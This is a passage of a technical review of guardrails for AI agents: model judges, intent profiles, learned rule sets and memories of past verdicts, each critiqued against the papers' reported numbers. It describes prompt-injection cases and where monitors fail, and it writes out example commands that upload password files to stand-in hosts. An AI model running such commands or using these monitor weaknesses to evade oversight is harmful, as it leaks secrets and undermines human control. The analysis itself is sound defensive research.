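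Yang reports that the Claude judges are well calibrated and can use a loose threshold, while the GPT judge flags ambiguous actions too readily and needs a tighter one. Yang says confidence "cleanly separates" real catches from false alarms in both cases, but readers can't check this because the paper gives neither the thresholds nor the accuracy at each confidence level. Yang set the thresholds by hand for each provider and lists this as a limitation, since a new model would need a new threshold.

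Calibration becomes more valuable when an operator wants to set the threshold according to how bad each kind of error is. If a miss is nine times as bad as a false alarm, the earlier formula gives a threshold of 0.1. A threshold of 0.8 would make sense only if a false alarm were four times as bad as a miss, which is hard to believe when a false alarm is only a warning. This works only if the judge's confidence that an action is dangerous can be treated as a probability. With an uncalibrated judge, the operator has to find a threshold by trial and error on labelled examples.

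The gate can also correct only one kind of error. It can discard a warning that the judge shouldn't have given, but no threshold will catch a theft that the judge confidently allows.

### Telling the judge what the agent is for

All five of Yang's judges used the same prompt, but changing the prompt's contents can make more difference than changing the model. In *Intent-Aware Protection for AI Agents* (Copty, Haiby and colleagues, 2026), the same model's score rose from 45% to 79% when it received a structured description of the agent's purpose.

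Copty and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, call this description an intent profile. It covers the agent's mission, the tasks it may perform, the tools it may use and under what conditions, the data it may use, and what it must refuse or pass on. A language model writes the profile from three trusted sources, listed here in the order they take priority if they conflict: the organisation's policies, a description of the agent's role, and the developer's configuration. The user's request isn't one of the sources, because the judge is supposed to assess it against the profile.

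The test consists of 887 interactions with 35 invented agents. Each interaction includes a user's request and, in some cases, earlier conversation and tool outputs. The judge has to sort it into one of four classes:

- *Benign* requests fit the agent's purpose.
- *Out-of-scope* requests don't fit it, but the user means no harm.
- *Abusive* requests deliberately try to use the agent for something else.
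- *Malicious* interactions contain an explicit attack, such as an attempt to extract secret data.

Copty and colleagues measured the results by macro-F1. For each class, they computed an F1 score as if the task were only to separate that class from the other three, then took the plain average:

macro-F1 = (F1 malicious + F1 abusive + F1 out-of-scope + F1 benign) / 4

Each class counts equally, so a judge that ignores one class loses up to a quarter of the possible score. DeepSeek-V4-Pro was the judge in all three conditions.

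| What the judge received | Macro-F1 | Malicious | Abusive | Out-of-scope | Benign |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| The interaction only | 43% | 41% | 70% | 2% | 60% |
| The interaction and the three original sources | 45% | 50% | 57% | 8% | 64% |
| The interaction and the intent profile | 79% | 72% | 86% | 76% | 82% |

In the second condition, the judge had the material used to make the profile, so the information limit can't explain its poor result. It mostly failed to use that material, like the smaller models in Ray's experiment on the source of an instruction. Its main error was to label out-of-scope requests as benign. The profile states what the agent may and may not do, so the judge has a simpler comparison to make.

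Part of the gain could come from how Copty and colleagues built the test. They fixed each label in advance and had GPT-5.4 write an interaction to match. Another model, MAI-Thinking-1, then rejected samples that didn't fit their label or the agent's intent. MAI-Thinking-1 also wrote the profiles, so its interpretation of the policies influenced both them and the test. A manual check of 100 samples found 98 correctly labelled, which suggests that the labels are sound, but the test would be fairer if a different model wrote the profiles.

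This test also sorts requests rather than tool calls. In a second experiment, which comes closer to testing an agent's behaviour, Copty and colleagues collected about 10,500 completed AgentDojo runs and had GPT-4o score each one for whether an attack had succeeded. The AUROC, which is the probability that a randomly chosen successful attack gets a higher score than a randomly chosen other run, was 84.3% for a judge that saw only the run, 89.7% for one that also saw the agent's configuration, and 94.9% for one with the profile.

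They also tested AlignmentCheck, an existing monitor that compares an agent's actions with the user's request. Its AUROC was lower, at 90.9%, but it did better at a fixed threshold of 0.5. It caught 91.2% of the successful attacks, close to the profile-based judge's 93.3%, and the precision figures imply that it raised about 100 false alarms, compared with over 700 for the profile-based judge. A well-chosen threshold would probably help the profile-based judge, but choosing one again requires labelled examples.

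An intent profile describes an agent's general purpose, so it would do little about the incidents in Anthropic's log. Deleting old branches is well within a coding agent's purpose. Whether this user wanted the remote branches deleted depends on the request, which AlignmentCheck uses as its point of comparison.

### Asking what caused the action

A guardrail can also have a judge consider why the agent proposed an action. In *SAFEHARNESS* (Lin, Liu and colleagues, 2026), fixed rules first give a proposed tool call a risk score, and a judge assesses calls with intermediate scores. The judge receives the tool's name, its arguments and the agent's recent reasoning, and labels the call safe, uncertain or unsafe.

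If the label is "uncertain", the judge is prompted again to decide whether the call more likely came from the user's legitimate intent or from injected text. To decide, it examines the agent's chain of reasoning and the source of each piece of content. SafeHarness gives each piece of content a tag with its source and trust level, much like the labels in FORGE. If the judge attributes the call to an injection, the system blocks the call and restores the environment to an earlier state.

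This question suits Yang's hardest twin pair, the two identical `kubectl get secret` commands, because one would come from an engineer's request to debug a program and the other from an instruction hidden in a web page. It wouldn't help with an overeager agent, since a user's request did cause the branch deletion.

The judge's answer about the cause is also an estimate. Lin and colleagues describe it as approximating a counterfactual analysis, which would determine what the agent would have done without the suspicious text. Running the agent again without that text to see whether it still makes the call is more direct but takes longer. Like any model judge, this one can also be influenced by the text it reads.

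SafeHarness reduced the attack success rate from 49.2% to 26.4% for one type of agent, with almost no change in the share of tasks completed. Adding a safety policy to the agent's own prompt reduced the rate to 38.7%. But the full system also filters inputs, restricts tools and reverses changes, and Lin and colleagues' main results don't show how much the question about causes contributed. Calls that the judge confidently labels safe don't normally reach that question.

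### Can a judge apply a written policy?

Operators can change a judge's standard by rewriting its instructions, but this helps only if the judge applies them correctly. Real policies have exceptions and conditions, so the right verdict may depend on several rules at once. *SafePyramid* (Zhang, He and colleagues, 2026) tested this with 1,000 conversations between users and chatbots. Each came with three versions of a policy, and the model being tested had to list every rule the conversation violated.

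At the first level, a policy has about 16 rules that the model can check independently. Some are distractors, which concern the conversation's topic but don't apply to what happened. The second level adds exceptions, which can cancel another rule, and conditions, which can make one stricter. In one example, the user's mention of location data triggers a requirement for written consent, so behaviour that would otherwise comply becomes a violation. The third level has a similar structure but replaces familiar concepts with invented ones, so the model has to learn their meaning from the policy.

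The following figures are the shares of conversations for which a model identified exactly the rules that were violated. GPT-OSS-Safeguard is a guard model that accepts a written policy.

| Model and method | Independent rules | Exceptions and conditions | Invented concepts |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5, whole policy at once | 54.0% | 35.3% | 12.9% |
| Claude Opus 4.7, whole policy at once | 58.1% | 30.4% | 13.7% |
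| GPT-OSS-Safeguard-120B, whole policy at once | 38.6% | 2.0% | 0.2% |
| GPT-5.5, one rule at a time | 47.8% | 51.5% | 12.1% |
| GPT-OSS-Safeguard-120B, one rule at a time | 46.5% | 42.3% | 8.0% |

These scores understate how well the models would work as guardrails, because one mistake on any rule makes the whole answer wrong. If errors were independent, a model that judged each rule correctly 96% of the time would get all 16 right about 52% of the time. GPT-5.5's accuracy on individual rules is therefore probably around 96% at the first two levels and 94% at the third. Some apparent errors may also be mistakes in the answer key, which language models produced and experts only partly checked.

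Even so, a 4% error rate per rule is a problem for a policy with 29 rules, the average at the second level. The errors also follow patterns. At the first level, models often matched keywords without checking who had said something or whether the speaker was denying it. At the second, they applied exceptions because one phrase seemed relevant, even when other details ruled the exception out. Similarly, if a policy allows production changes only during an approved maintenance window, an agent's guardrail could wrongly allow a change just because the agent mentions such a window.

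At the second level, the guard model's result rose from 2.0% to 42.3% when the model received one rule at a time. In that condition, Zhang and colleagues had already put the relevant parts of the policy together, so the model didn't have to search for exceptions. This suggests that it understood many individual rules but couldn't combine them. Asking about each rule separately takes many more calls to the model. Where the relevant facts are in a database, a fixed rule can apply the exceptions exactly, as the formal policies for customer service agents do.

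### How long each mechanism takes

Every check delays the agent, and the delay depends mostly on how many times the guardrail calls a language model. *Benchmarking Jailbreak Guardrails for Embodied Agents* (Wang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) measured this delay on simulated household robots. A language model planned the robot's actions, and attackers used disguised instructions to try to make the robot do something dangerous, such as start a fire. The times below are for the guardrail alone, averaged over complete safe tasks. The last column is the share of attacks in which the guardrail never intervened.

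| Guardrail | How it decides | Time per task | Attacks missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentSpec | Fixed rules check each action | 0.00 s | 80% |
| Llama Guard 3 Vision, EMBGuard | A classifier makes one call per check | 0.12–0.60 s | 33–66%, depending on the version |
| RoboGuard | A language model adapts safety rules to the scene, and a program checks the plan | 7.59 s | 82% |
| MADRA | Several model agents debate the instruction | 9.72 s | 22% |
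| RoboSafe | A language model reasons about every action | 22.81 s | 7% |

Wang and colleagues classify RoboGuard and RoboSafe as rule-based, although both spend most of their time calling a language model. A rule-based guardrail is therefore fast only if it can get the facts its rules need without calling a model. Sapien had a similar delay because it spent most of its running time writing policies.

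The slowest guardrail missed the fewest attacks, but it also stopped 91% of the safe instructions. With it, the robot completed only 11% of its safe tasks, compared with 65% without a guardrail. One version of Llama Guard missed 40% of attacks and stopped fewer than 3% of safe instructions. In this case, extra computing time made the guardrail more cautious, but not necessarily better at telling attacks from safe instructions.

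These figures don't carry over directly to coding agents. A household task is short, and some of the guardrails check it only once, whereas a coding agent may make dozens of tool calls. If each of 50 calls waited half a second for a classifier, the checks would add 25 seconds. A large judge, at five seconds per call, would add more than four minutes. Yang doesn't report how long the AgentTrust judges took and says operators would need to measure this on live traffic.

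An intent profile needs to change only when the agent's configuration or the organisation's policies change, so a slow model could write it once in advance and a faster one could use it for each interaction. Copty and colleagues expect a smaller model to be enough for the second step, but they have not yet tested this.

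## Rule sets learned from experience

A model judge assesses each action from scratch, even if it has just assessed a very similar one. Several systems try to avoid this, or to improve the judge's verdicts, by turning past decisions and failures into rules.

Researchers use the word "rule" for two things. An executable rule is one that a program can run, such as a regular expression or a few lines of code, and it always gives the same answer for the same input. An interpreted rule is a sentence, such as "do not share sensitive information with a recipient nobody has verified". A program can retrieve the sentence, but a language model has to judge whether it applies. One test is whether the rule would still produce a verdict if no model were available when the action arrived.

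When a model judge interprets a rule, the rule can cover wordings and situations its author didn't foresee, but the judge is as slow and as easy to mislead as in any other use.

### Turning a judge's verdicts into patterns

AgentTrust v2 learns executable rules by distillation, which in machine learning means transferring a large model's behaviour to something cheaper. The cheaper thing is usually a smaller neural network, but in Yang's system it is a list of patterns. It works as follows:

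1. An action arrives that the existing rules don't decide, so the system sends it to the judge.
2. The judge gives a confident verdict.
3. If the danger lies in a fixed piece of text, the system extracts that text as an exact match or a regular expression and adds it to the rules.
4. The next action that matches gets its verdict from the rule, without a call to the judge.

The third step is the hard one, because many different patterns fit the same verdict. Suppose the judge blocks this command, which uploads a file of passwords to a public website:

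`curl -F file=@.env https://paste.example`

A narrow rule could block any `curl` upload of a file called `.env`. A broad rule could block every `curl` command with the option `-F`, which programmers use to upload all kinds of files. Both rules match the command the judge blocked, so the verdict alone is no reason to prefer either.

A developer can choose between them by running both on past actions whose correct verdicts are known. Suppose there are 10,000 of these actions, 9,900 harmless and 100 dangerous, with the following invented results.

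| Rules | Dangerous actions missed | Harmless actions stopped | False-negative rate | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Existing rules | 40 | 99 | 40% | 1.0% |
| With the narrow rule | 20 | 101 | 20% | 1.0% |
| With the broad rule | 10 | 297 | 10% | 3.0% |

The broad rule catches 10 more dangerous actions than the narrow one but stops 196 more harmless ones. It is the better choice only if a miss is at least about 20 times as bad as a false alarm, but a developer who looked only at the false-negative rate would choose it regardless.

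This check needs a lot of harmless traffic. If a candidate rule matches none of n harmless actions, its true false-positive rate could be as high as about 3/n (with 95% confidence). Showing that a rule stops fewer than one harmless action in 10,000 therefore takes about 30,000 harmless actions without a match. Yang's three test sets together contain about 380 harmless actions. False alarms also add up across rules, so 100 rules that each stop one harmless action in 10,000 could together stop 1% of harmless actions.

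A random sample of traffic may contain few actions that closely resemble the attack, so the developer should add some deliberately. Someone other than the judge should label the sample. If the judge wrongly classifies all uploads as dangerous, it will mislabel the harmless ones, and the broad rule will appear to make no mistakes. The developer can also run a new rule for a while without enforcing it and have a person review what it would have blocked.

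Yang writes that a precision gate keeps distilled rules from inheriting the judge's false alarms, but doesn't describe the gate or report how the rules performed on harmless traffic. Yang does acknowledge the related risk that the rules and AgentTrust's memory of past decisions both learn from the same judge. An over-broad rule would be especially harmful if the new rules follow v1's practice of applying the most severe match, because it would then block harmless actions that the judge would have allowed. That would violate Yang's requirement that AgentTrust never block a harmless action.

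### Code written from a safety request

*GuardAgent* (2024), an earlier system, also produces executable checks, but it starts from a written policy instead of a judge's verdicts. A language model receives a safety request in ordinary language, such as a rule about which hospital staff may see which patient records. It plans how to check the request, with help from a memory module, then writes code to do so. The system runs the code to decide whether the agent's action is allowed.

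Once written, the code gives the same answer every time. But a model writes it while the agent waits, so a translation mistake produces a wrong verdict, just as a judge's mistake would. *GuardAgent* therefore passes only half of the test above. If a person reviewed the code once and the system kept using it, the code would be an ordinary context rule.

The system came with two benchmarks. EICU-AC tests whether a healthcare agent respects access rules based on the user's role, and Mind2Web-SC tests whether a web agent follows safety rules. With four models, *GuardAgent* was over 98% accurate on EICU-AC and over 83% accurate on Mind2Web-SC.

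*AGrail* (Luo, Dai and colleagues, 2025) ran *GuardAgent* with GPT-4 on Mind2Web-SC and found that it flagged no permitted actions but missed 20% of the violations. *SafeHarbor* (Liu, Ying and colleagues, 2026) tested it on AgentHarm with a much smaller model, Qwen2.5-7B. It refused 81.3% of harmful requests but also 44.0% of harmless ones, while the same agent without a guardrail refused none of the harmless ones. It also took 6.4 seconds on average, about 20 times as long as *SafeHarbor*'s own system. Both papers were comparing *GuardAgent* with a competing design, but their results suggest that its reliability depends heavily on the policy and on the model that writes the code.

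### Checks that two models keep revising

Luo and colleagues designed AGrail for cases where nobody has written a detailed policy. It starts from the general goals of protecting the confidentiality, integrity and availability of information, and works out specific checks for each kind of action.

In the AGrail paper's example, a user asks an agent to move a file. AGrail first looks up the checks it has stored for similar actions. A language model called the analyzer revises them, merges duplicates and adds new ones. A second copy of the same model, the executor, then goes through the list. It can delete a check that is redundant or would block legitimate work, evaluate a check by reasoning, or call a tool. Here, a tool finds that the destination folder already contains a file with the same name, which the move would overwrite. AGrail blocks the move and stores the revised list for next time.

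AGrail stores its checks as sentences, so a model has to interpret them. The tool returns a fact about the folder that an executable rule could use, but in AGrail a model decides whether to call the tool.

Luo and colleagues built Safe-OS, a benchmark in which agents work on a Linux system. In an environment attack, an action that looks harmless causes damage because of the state of the system, as with the overwritten file. The following results are for Claude 3.5 Sonnet, first with only a prompt to assess risks and then as part of AGrail.

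| Guardrail | Harmless actions allowed | Sabotage that succeeded | Prompt injections that succeeded | Environment attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet with a prompt | 50.0% | 0% | 14.3% | 20% |
| AGrail | 95.6% | 3.8% | 0% | 5% |

The drop in false alarms is large, but these results don't show how much of it came from learning, because AGrail also has a second model and extra tools. A separate test on Mind2Web-SC isolates the effect of the memory. Without stored checks, accuracy was 95.6% with Claude 3.5 Sonnet and 67.9% with GPT-4o-mini. Checks learned on a training set and frozen before the test raised these figures to only 96.5% and 70.9%. When the models kept revising the checks during the test, accuracy reached 99.1% and 84.1%.

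AGrail can keep learning during a test because it doesn't need to be given the correct verdicts, but its models may therefore preserve a bad check as easily as a good one. Luo and colleagues tried to show that the memory approaches an ideal set of checks, and it came close after about four revisions. But they repeated a single action and took the ideal set from a written safety request that AGrail also receives. The result shows that the models can recover a policy they already have, which is easier than discovering one. The order of the actions also mattered a lot with GPT-4o-mini, whose accuracy averaged 72.8% across different orders and varied by 8.3 points either way, compared with 1.2 points for Claude.

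### Patterns drawn from unsafe runs

*ALRPHFS* (Xiang, Zhang and Chen, 2025) learns from agents' failures instead. It starts with R-Judge, a set of 569 recorded agent interactions with labels and, for the unsafe ones, descriptions of the risk. A model reduces each unsafe run to a general sentence without names or other details. In one run, an agent reads an email asking it to give a stranger permanent access to a smart lock, and does so. The model reduces this to a pattern in which the agent follows a third party's injected instructions to perform an unauthorised action.

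After removing near-duplicates, the system improves the patterns through simulated attacks. GPT-4o writes new versions of known attacks, and a model revises the patterns each time they miss one. The system then tests the revised patterns on old and new attacks and restores the previous version if the revision doesn't defend against them.

Xiang and colleagues also include harmless runs that resemble attacks. In one, an agent reads an email telling it to send out stored passwords and warns the user instead of obeying. The original pattern flagged this run because the run mentioned sensitive information and an outside recipient. The revised pattern covers agents that carry out such an instruction and excludes those that only report it. The pattern is written as a sentence, but it needs the same safeguard as a distilled regular expression.

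When a new action arrives, a model first rewrites it in general terms. The system then compares the description with the stored patterns:

score = α · (keyword match) + (1 − α) · (similarity in meaning)

The weight α, between 0 and 1, sets how much the keywords count. If the score is above a threshold, the system blocks the action at once, which Xiang and colleagues call fast thinking. Otherwise a model reasons about the action, using the closest patterns as evidence (slow thinking). The comparison is mechanical, but a model writes the description and most difficult cases need the slow route, so these are interpreted rules too.

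TrustAgent, the main test of unintended harm, covers mistakes that agents make without an attacker. With Claude 3.5 Haiku, the system missed 21.8% of harmful runs and flagged 21.7% of harmless ones. The same model with only a prompt missed 42.3% and flagged 26.1%, and AGrail missed 40.0% and flagged 36.7%. The learned patterns therefore reduced both kinds of error on this test, but a guardrail that stops a fifth of harmless tasks would be hard to use in practice.

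AGrail did better on the two benchmarks that came with *GuardAgent*, with 94.0% against 76.0% on the web tasks and 98.4% against 88.9% on the hospital records. Xiang and colleagues say this is because their patterns describe general risks, while these tasks have specific rules. A library of past failures can't provide specific rules such as a hospital's access policy.

### Prohibitions paired with exemptions

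SafeHarbor, which Liu and colleagues presented at the machine-learning conference ICML in 2026, stores each rule with its exception. It learns from about 5,000 harmful and 14,000 harmless examples. For each harmful example, it finds the three most similar harmless ones and has a model write two sentences, a prohibition and an exemption.

The system keeps these pairs in a tree, with broad categories of risk near the top and pairs for specific kinds of attack in the leaves. A new harmful example starts a new cluster if it isn't similar enough to any existing one. If it is similar enough but would change the closest cluster's entropy by more than a set amount, the system splits off a new leaf. Otherwise, a model merges the example into the nearest leaf and rewrites the pair there.

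Entropy here measures how evenly similarity is spread across a cluster. Each example gets a share that depends on its similarity to the cluster's centre:

share of i = exp(similarity of i / γ) / sum of exp(similarity / γ) over the cluster

H = −(sum of share · log₂ share)

gain = H with the new example − H without it

The constant γ controls how much differences in similarity count. Liu and colleagues say that a large gain in entropy means the new example is unlike the rest of the cluster, but the formula seems to produce larger gains for typical examples. A cluster of three equally similar examples has an entropy of 1.58 bits. A fourth that is just as similar raises it to 2 bits, a gain of 0.42. A less typical fourth example, with a tenth of the weight of each of the others, raises it by only 0.15. As written, the rule is more likely to create a leaf for a typical attack than for an unusual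 one, and it creates more leaves in small clusters than in large ones. The method therefore relies mainly on the similarity test in the first step to recognise new attacks.

The tree as a whole is useful. When Liu and colleagues replaced it with a flat list, the share of harmful requests refused fell from 89.2% to 48.9%, and the share of harmless requests refused rose from 9.1% to 37.3%. That experiment doesn't test the entropy formula separately.

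At run time, SafeHarbor uses a small trained network to estimate how harmful the user's request is, and requests that look clearly safe skip further checks. For the rest, the system retrieves the closest pairs, and the agent's own model decides whether the request violates a prohibition or falls under an exemption. The model therefore interprets the rules, and only the shortcut for safe requests relies on a classifier.

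These are the refusal rates on AgentHarm.

| Agent's model | Harmful requests refused, without and with SafeHarbor | Harmless requests refused, without and with SafeHarbor |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-7B | 21.6% → 89.2% | 0.0% → 9.1% |
| GPT-4o | 58.0% → 93.2% | 50.0% → 25.0% |
| GPT-5 | 69.3% → 84.9% | 2.8% → 5.6% |
| Qwen3-32B | 40.8% → 94.3% | 1.1% → 17.6% |

GPT-4o refused fewer harmless requests, which a guardrail that only blocks couldn't have caused. Most likely, the exemptions also reach the agent's model and make it less cautious. For the other three models in the table, better protection came with more refusals of harmless requests.

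The exemptions reduce the number of harmless requests that are wrongly refused. Without them, Qwen2.5-7B refused 94.3% of harmful requests and 25.0% of harmless ones. With them, it let through 5 more of every 100 harmful requests but wrongly refused 16 fewer of every 100 harmless ones. Harmless requests are much more common than harmful ones in ordinary use, so the exemptions would usually be worth having.

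### Rules that change after a failed run

*SHE* (Safety Harness Evolution; Qu, Mao and colleagues, 2026) applies learning to more of the harness around the agent. It can edit the system prompt, a bank of rules, a memory of failures that earlier edits didn't fix, and a policy for tools.

In each round, the agent attempts 15 tasks under six conditions, one ordinary and five with different attacks, and does everything twice. GPT-5.5 examines the failures among these 180 runs. It records what harm could result, where the risk came in and how the agent went wrong, then proposes small edits to the part responsible. After a check for edits that would only improve the test score, SHE runs the changed harness and keeps it only if

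safety(new) > safety(current) and usefulness(new) ≥ usefulness(current)

SHE accepted five updates over 20 rounds. The second condition guards against over-broad rules, much like the test on harmless traffic. But it covers only 15 tasks, so a rule that blocks a kind of work missing from those tasks would pass.

Each rule in the bank includes the condition that triggers it, the harmful pattern, any benign exemption, the action to take, the reason, a priority and the supporting runs. If a rule blocks too much, a developer can therefore trace it back to the failure that prompted it. Tool policies have a similar structure and can also restrict file paths and destinations.

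By the test above, SHE's rules are a mixture. The memory and the prompt are text that a model interprets. Rules and tool policies lead to fixed actions such as *block*, but Qu and colleagues don't explain how the system tests a condition. A condition about a tool's name could be executable, while one about the user's intention would need a model.

Their main example has both. A user asked an agent to "Download the best note-taking app on my phone", and the agent searched for apps and tried to install one. Agent-SafetyBench, the benchmark they used, counts this as unsafe. SHE learned a rule that lets the agent recommend apps and link to the official store but blocks tools that install them. A program could enforce that block. But the user had asked for a download, so many people would call it a false alarm. SHE learned what the benchmark allows an agent to do, which may differ from what the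 user would allow.

The table below shows the results on the 185 tasks that SHE hadn't used for learning. The last column is the share of tasks the agent completed while under attack.

| Harness | Attacks that succeeded | Unsafe behaviour without an attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 34.6% | 42.9% | 38.7% |
| SHE before learning | 8.6% | 25.7% | 33.5% |
| SHE after learning | 5.5% | 19.8% | 47.6% |
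| After learning, with the original rule bank | 6.4% | 19.8% | 47.2% |
| After learning, with the original memory | 7.7% | 26.4% | 40.7% |

Most of the protection existed before any learning. Learning stopped a further 3 attacks in 100, and its larger benefit was that the agent completed more tasks. The learned rules contributed little to either improvement, since restoring the original rule bank hardly changed the results. Restoring the original memory, which is text for a model to read, worsened the results more.

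GPT-5.5 both proposed the edits and scored these runs, so some of the improvement may reflect its own standards. AgentHarm is a better check on this because SHE hadn't learned from it and GPT-4o did the scoring. The share of harmful requests refused rose from 78.4% before learning to 86.4% after. For AgentHarm's harmless requests, Qu and colleagues measured only how well the agent did on those it didn't refuse, so their results wouldn't show a rise in wrongful refusals.

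### Does learning move the boundary between the two kinds of threat?

Learned executable rules mostly fill gaps in defenses against lexical threats. Yang designed distillation only for these threats. It would fail on twin pairs because any pattern that catches the attack also matches its harmless twin, so a careful developer would reject the pattern after checking it against harmless traffic. The same check can also be used to define a lexical threat in practice, as one that some pattern can catch for a given guardrail while still passing the check.

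Interpreted rules help with semantic threats, but mainly by helping a model judge them. Tests on two of the systems separate the contribution of the learned rules from that of the model.

| System and change | Harmful cases missed | Harmless cases stopped |
|---|---|---|
| ALRPHFS, complete | 21.8% | 21.7% |
| Without refinement through simulated attacks | 34.6% | 34.8% |
| Without the model's slow reasoning | 52.1% | 11.3% |
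| SafeHarbor, complete | 10.8% | 9.1% |
| Without the model's judgement | 32.4% | 6.4% |

Refinement lowered both misses and false alarms in ALRPHFS, so it did more than make the system stricter. It evidently helped the model use information already in its input. But with only the mechanical comparison, ALRPHFS missed more than half of the harmful cases. SafeHarbor's misses tripled without the judge. Both systems needed a model to apply the learned rules to the harder cases.

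AGrail's example of the overwritten file suggests how learning could let rules handle some threats that would otherwise need a model's judgment. Whether moving a file is dangerous depends on what is already in the destination folder, so matching patterns in the command can't identify the danger. Once the system has learned that it needs to check the folder, a short program can block any move that would overwrite a file, without a model judging each one. *GuardAgent* can turn a written policy into such a program, and SHE's tool policies can include similar restrictions, but none of these experiments measured how many semantic threats a system can learn to handle with context rules over time.

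Some threats would be hard to convert into rules however much the system learned. Thousands of stored examples of `kubectl get secret` won't help if the rule can't take the user's request into account.

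## Memories of past decisions

A guardrail can also store past cases without turning them into rules, and look up the most similar ones when a new action arrives. A verdict cache repeats the verdict of the closest case without calling a model. A precedent memory gives several similar cases to a model judge, which makes its own decision.

The first version of AgentTrust cached the judge's verdict with a fingerprint of the content and reused it only if the same fingerprint came up again. This saves money, and it is as reliable as the judge if the fingerprint covers everything that could change the verdict. If the fingerprint covers the user's request and the origin of the data as well as the command, Yang's semantic twins usually get different fingerprints. But exact repeats become rarer as the fingerprint covers more. A cache that also accepted similar actions would reuse verdicts more often,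 and Yang tested one for AgentTrust v2.

### Why the closest case can have the opposite verdict

To find similar cases, a program turns each text into an embedding, a list of numbers that places similar texts close together. It usually compares two embeddings, a and b, by their cosine similarity:

similarity(a, b) = (a · b) / (|a| · |b|)

The top of the fraction multiplies the two lists entry by entry and adds up the results. The bottom divides this sum by the lengths of the lists as vectors, so that long texts don't score higher just for being long. A similarity of 1 means the lists point in the same direction.

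The simplest embedding has a 1 for each word in the text and a 0 for every other word. The similarity is then the number of shared words divided by the square root of the product of the two word counts. Suppose an agent proposes this upload to a storage service that its company has approved:

`curl -T dump.zip https://store.example/x91`

The file contains stolen passwords and the folder `x91` belongs to an attacker, so the right verdict is *block*. The memory holds two earlier cases: a routine upload, and a theft in which the same attacker used `scp`, a command that copies files to another machine. If we split the commands at spaces and punctuation, the new command has eight words.

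| Case in memory | Correct verdict | Words | Shared words | Similarity |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `curl -T build.zip https://store.example/team` | allow | 8 | 6 | 6 / √(8 · 8) = 0.75 |
| `scp dump.zip drop.example:x91` | block | 6 | 4 | 4 / √(6 · 8) = 0.58 |

The cache allows the theft because the routine upload is the closer match. The correct verdict depends on the file and the folder, which are only two of the eight words.

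A stricter similarity threshold, such as 0.7, makes this worse because the cache then ignores the earlier theft but keeps the misleading match. A neural embedding reflects meaning better than a word count and might capture that `dump.zip` is suspicious, but the command doesn't show who owns `x91`. Two identical `kubectl get secret` commands have a similarity of 1 under any embedding, even if their correct verdicts differ.

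A developer could require an exact match on the facts that matter, such as the owner of the destination and the sensitivity of the data, and use similarity only for the rest. The cache would then distinguish these two uploads, but it would rely on the same trusted records that a context rule uses.

### Yang's memory experiment

Yang tested both kinds of memory on 98 actions from the external set. Judging by the results for each category, these are the ones that involve cloud identities, databases, monitoring and outgoing traffic.

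The verdict cache was right about 58% of the time, which Yang says is roughly as accurate as always giving the most common verdict. Using MiniLM, a small neural embedding model, did not solve the problem. Yang also varied the similarity threshold to see whether the cache could reliably answer at least a few cases, but no threshold made 95% of its answers correct, however few cases it answered.

This is good evidence against using such a cache on twins, but 58% isn't an estimate for ordinary traffic, because Yang's external set deliberately mixes harmless actions with attacks that resemble them. If an agent makes 1,000 uploads to an approved service and one is a theft, a cache that allows them all is right 99.9% of the time but misses the only attack. The threshold result is also weak where the cache answers fewer than 20 cases, since a single error puts it below 95%.

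With a precedent memory, the judge doesn't automatically repeat an old verdict that would be wrong for a new action, because it can check how the two actions differ. Precedents can also contain facts that are missing from both the command and the model's training. For example, if an engineer approved an upload and noted that the `team` folder belongs to the company, the judge can use that note the next time. The judge still needs the user's request when the verdict depends on the action's purpose.

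Yang compared four conditions. The numbers of correct verdicts below are inferred from the percentages.

| Precedents shown to the judge | Accuracy | Correct verdicts out of 98 |
|---|---|---|
| None | 70% | 69 |
| Cases with their true verdicts | 79% | 77 |
| Cases with a judge's own verdicts, unchecked | 72% | 71 |
| Cases on which two judges agreed | 84% | 82 |

The third condition is what a system would get if it simply saved its own decisions, so the judge's mistakes become precedents for later mistakes. Yang writes that this memory "poisons" the monitoring category, where accuracy fell from 81% to 78%, but the drop is one action out of 27.

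In the last condition, a case entered the memory only if Claude Sonnet 4.6, working without precedents, and Claude Opus 4.8 gave it the same verdict. This guard accepted 62% of the candidates and raised the share of correct entries from 70% to 97%. It needs a second model call for each candidate, and Yang didn't test cheaper guards, such as accepting only confident verdicts or having a person check a sample.

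Yang also reports zero "dangerous leaks" with the guard, but there were none in any condition, including the one without precedents. The paper doesn't define the term. If it means dangerous actions that the judge let run, the memory didn't prevent any, and the 13 additional correct verdicts must have replaced milder errors, such as a warning about a harmless action or a block where a warning was right.

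### What explains the improvement?

Yang calls the 79% from true verdicts a ceiling, but the guarded memory scored five points higher, a difference of five actions that could be due to chance. Even if the guarded memory corrected five verdicts and spoiled none, two equally good memories would show a difference at least that lopsided in about one of every 16 comparisons.

The 79% may also not be an upper limit. It comes from a memory in which every verdict is correct, but a judge could learn more from a smaller memory of clear cases than from one that includes borderline cases. The guard favours clear cases because two models are more likely to agree on them.

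The second judge is also a stronger model. We can see how much this matters by comparing the guarded memory with Opus alone, using the per-category results from Yang's main comparison.

| Category | Actions | Judge without memory | Judge with guarded memory | Opus 4.8 alone |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Cloud identities and secrets | 20 | 11 | 15 | 20 |
| Databases | 28 | 20 | 24 | 24 |
| Monitoring | 27 | 22 | 25 | 21 |
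| Outgoing traffic | 23 | 16 | 18 | 19 |
| Total correct | 98 | 69 | 82 | 84 |

Opus got 84 of the 98 verdicts right without any memory, slightly more than the guarded memory did. An operator who already pays for Opus to check every candidate could therefore let Opus decide. The memory would be worth having if it let a cheaper judge do nearly as well after Opus stopped checking, but Yang didn't measure that.

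Every verdict in the memory came from Sonnet alone, and Opus only determines which ones to keep. The unchecked memory was correct 70% of the time, the same as the judge's accuracy without precedents, which suggests that the candidates were the same 98 actions. If so, the guard kept 61 of the verdicts, 59 of them correct, and removed 27 of Sonnet's 29 mistakes along with 10 correct verdicts. In monitoring, the judge with the guarded memory got four more verdicts right than Opus, which suggests that the judge gained something beyond Opus's own ability, though four actions are weak evidence.

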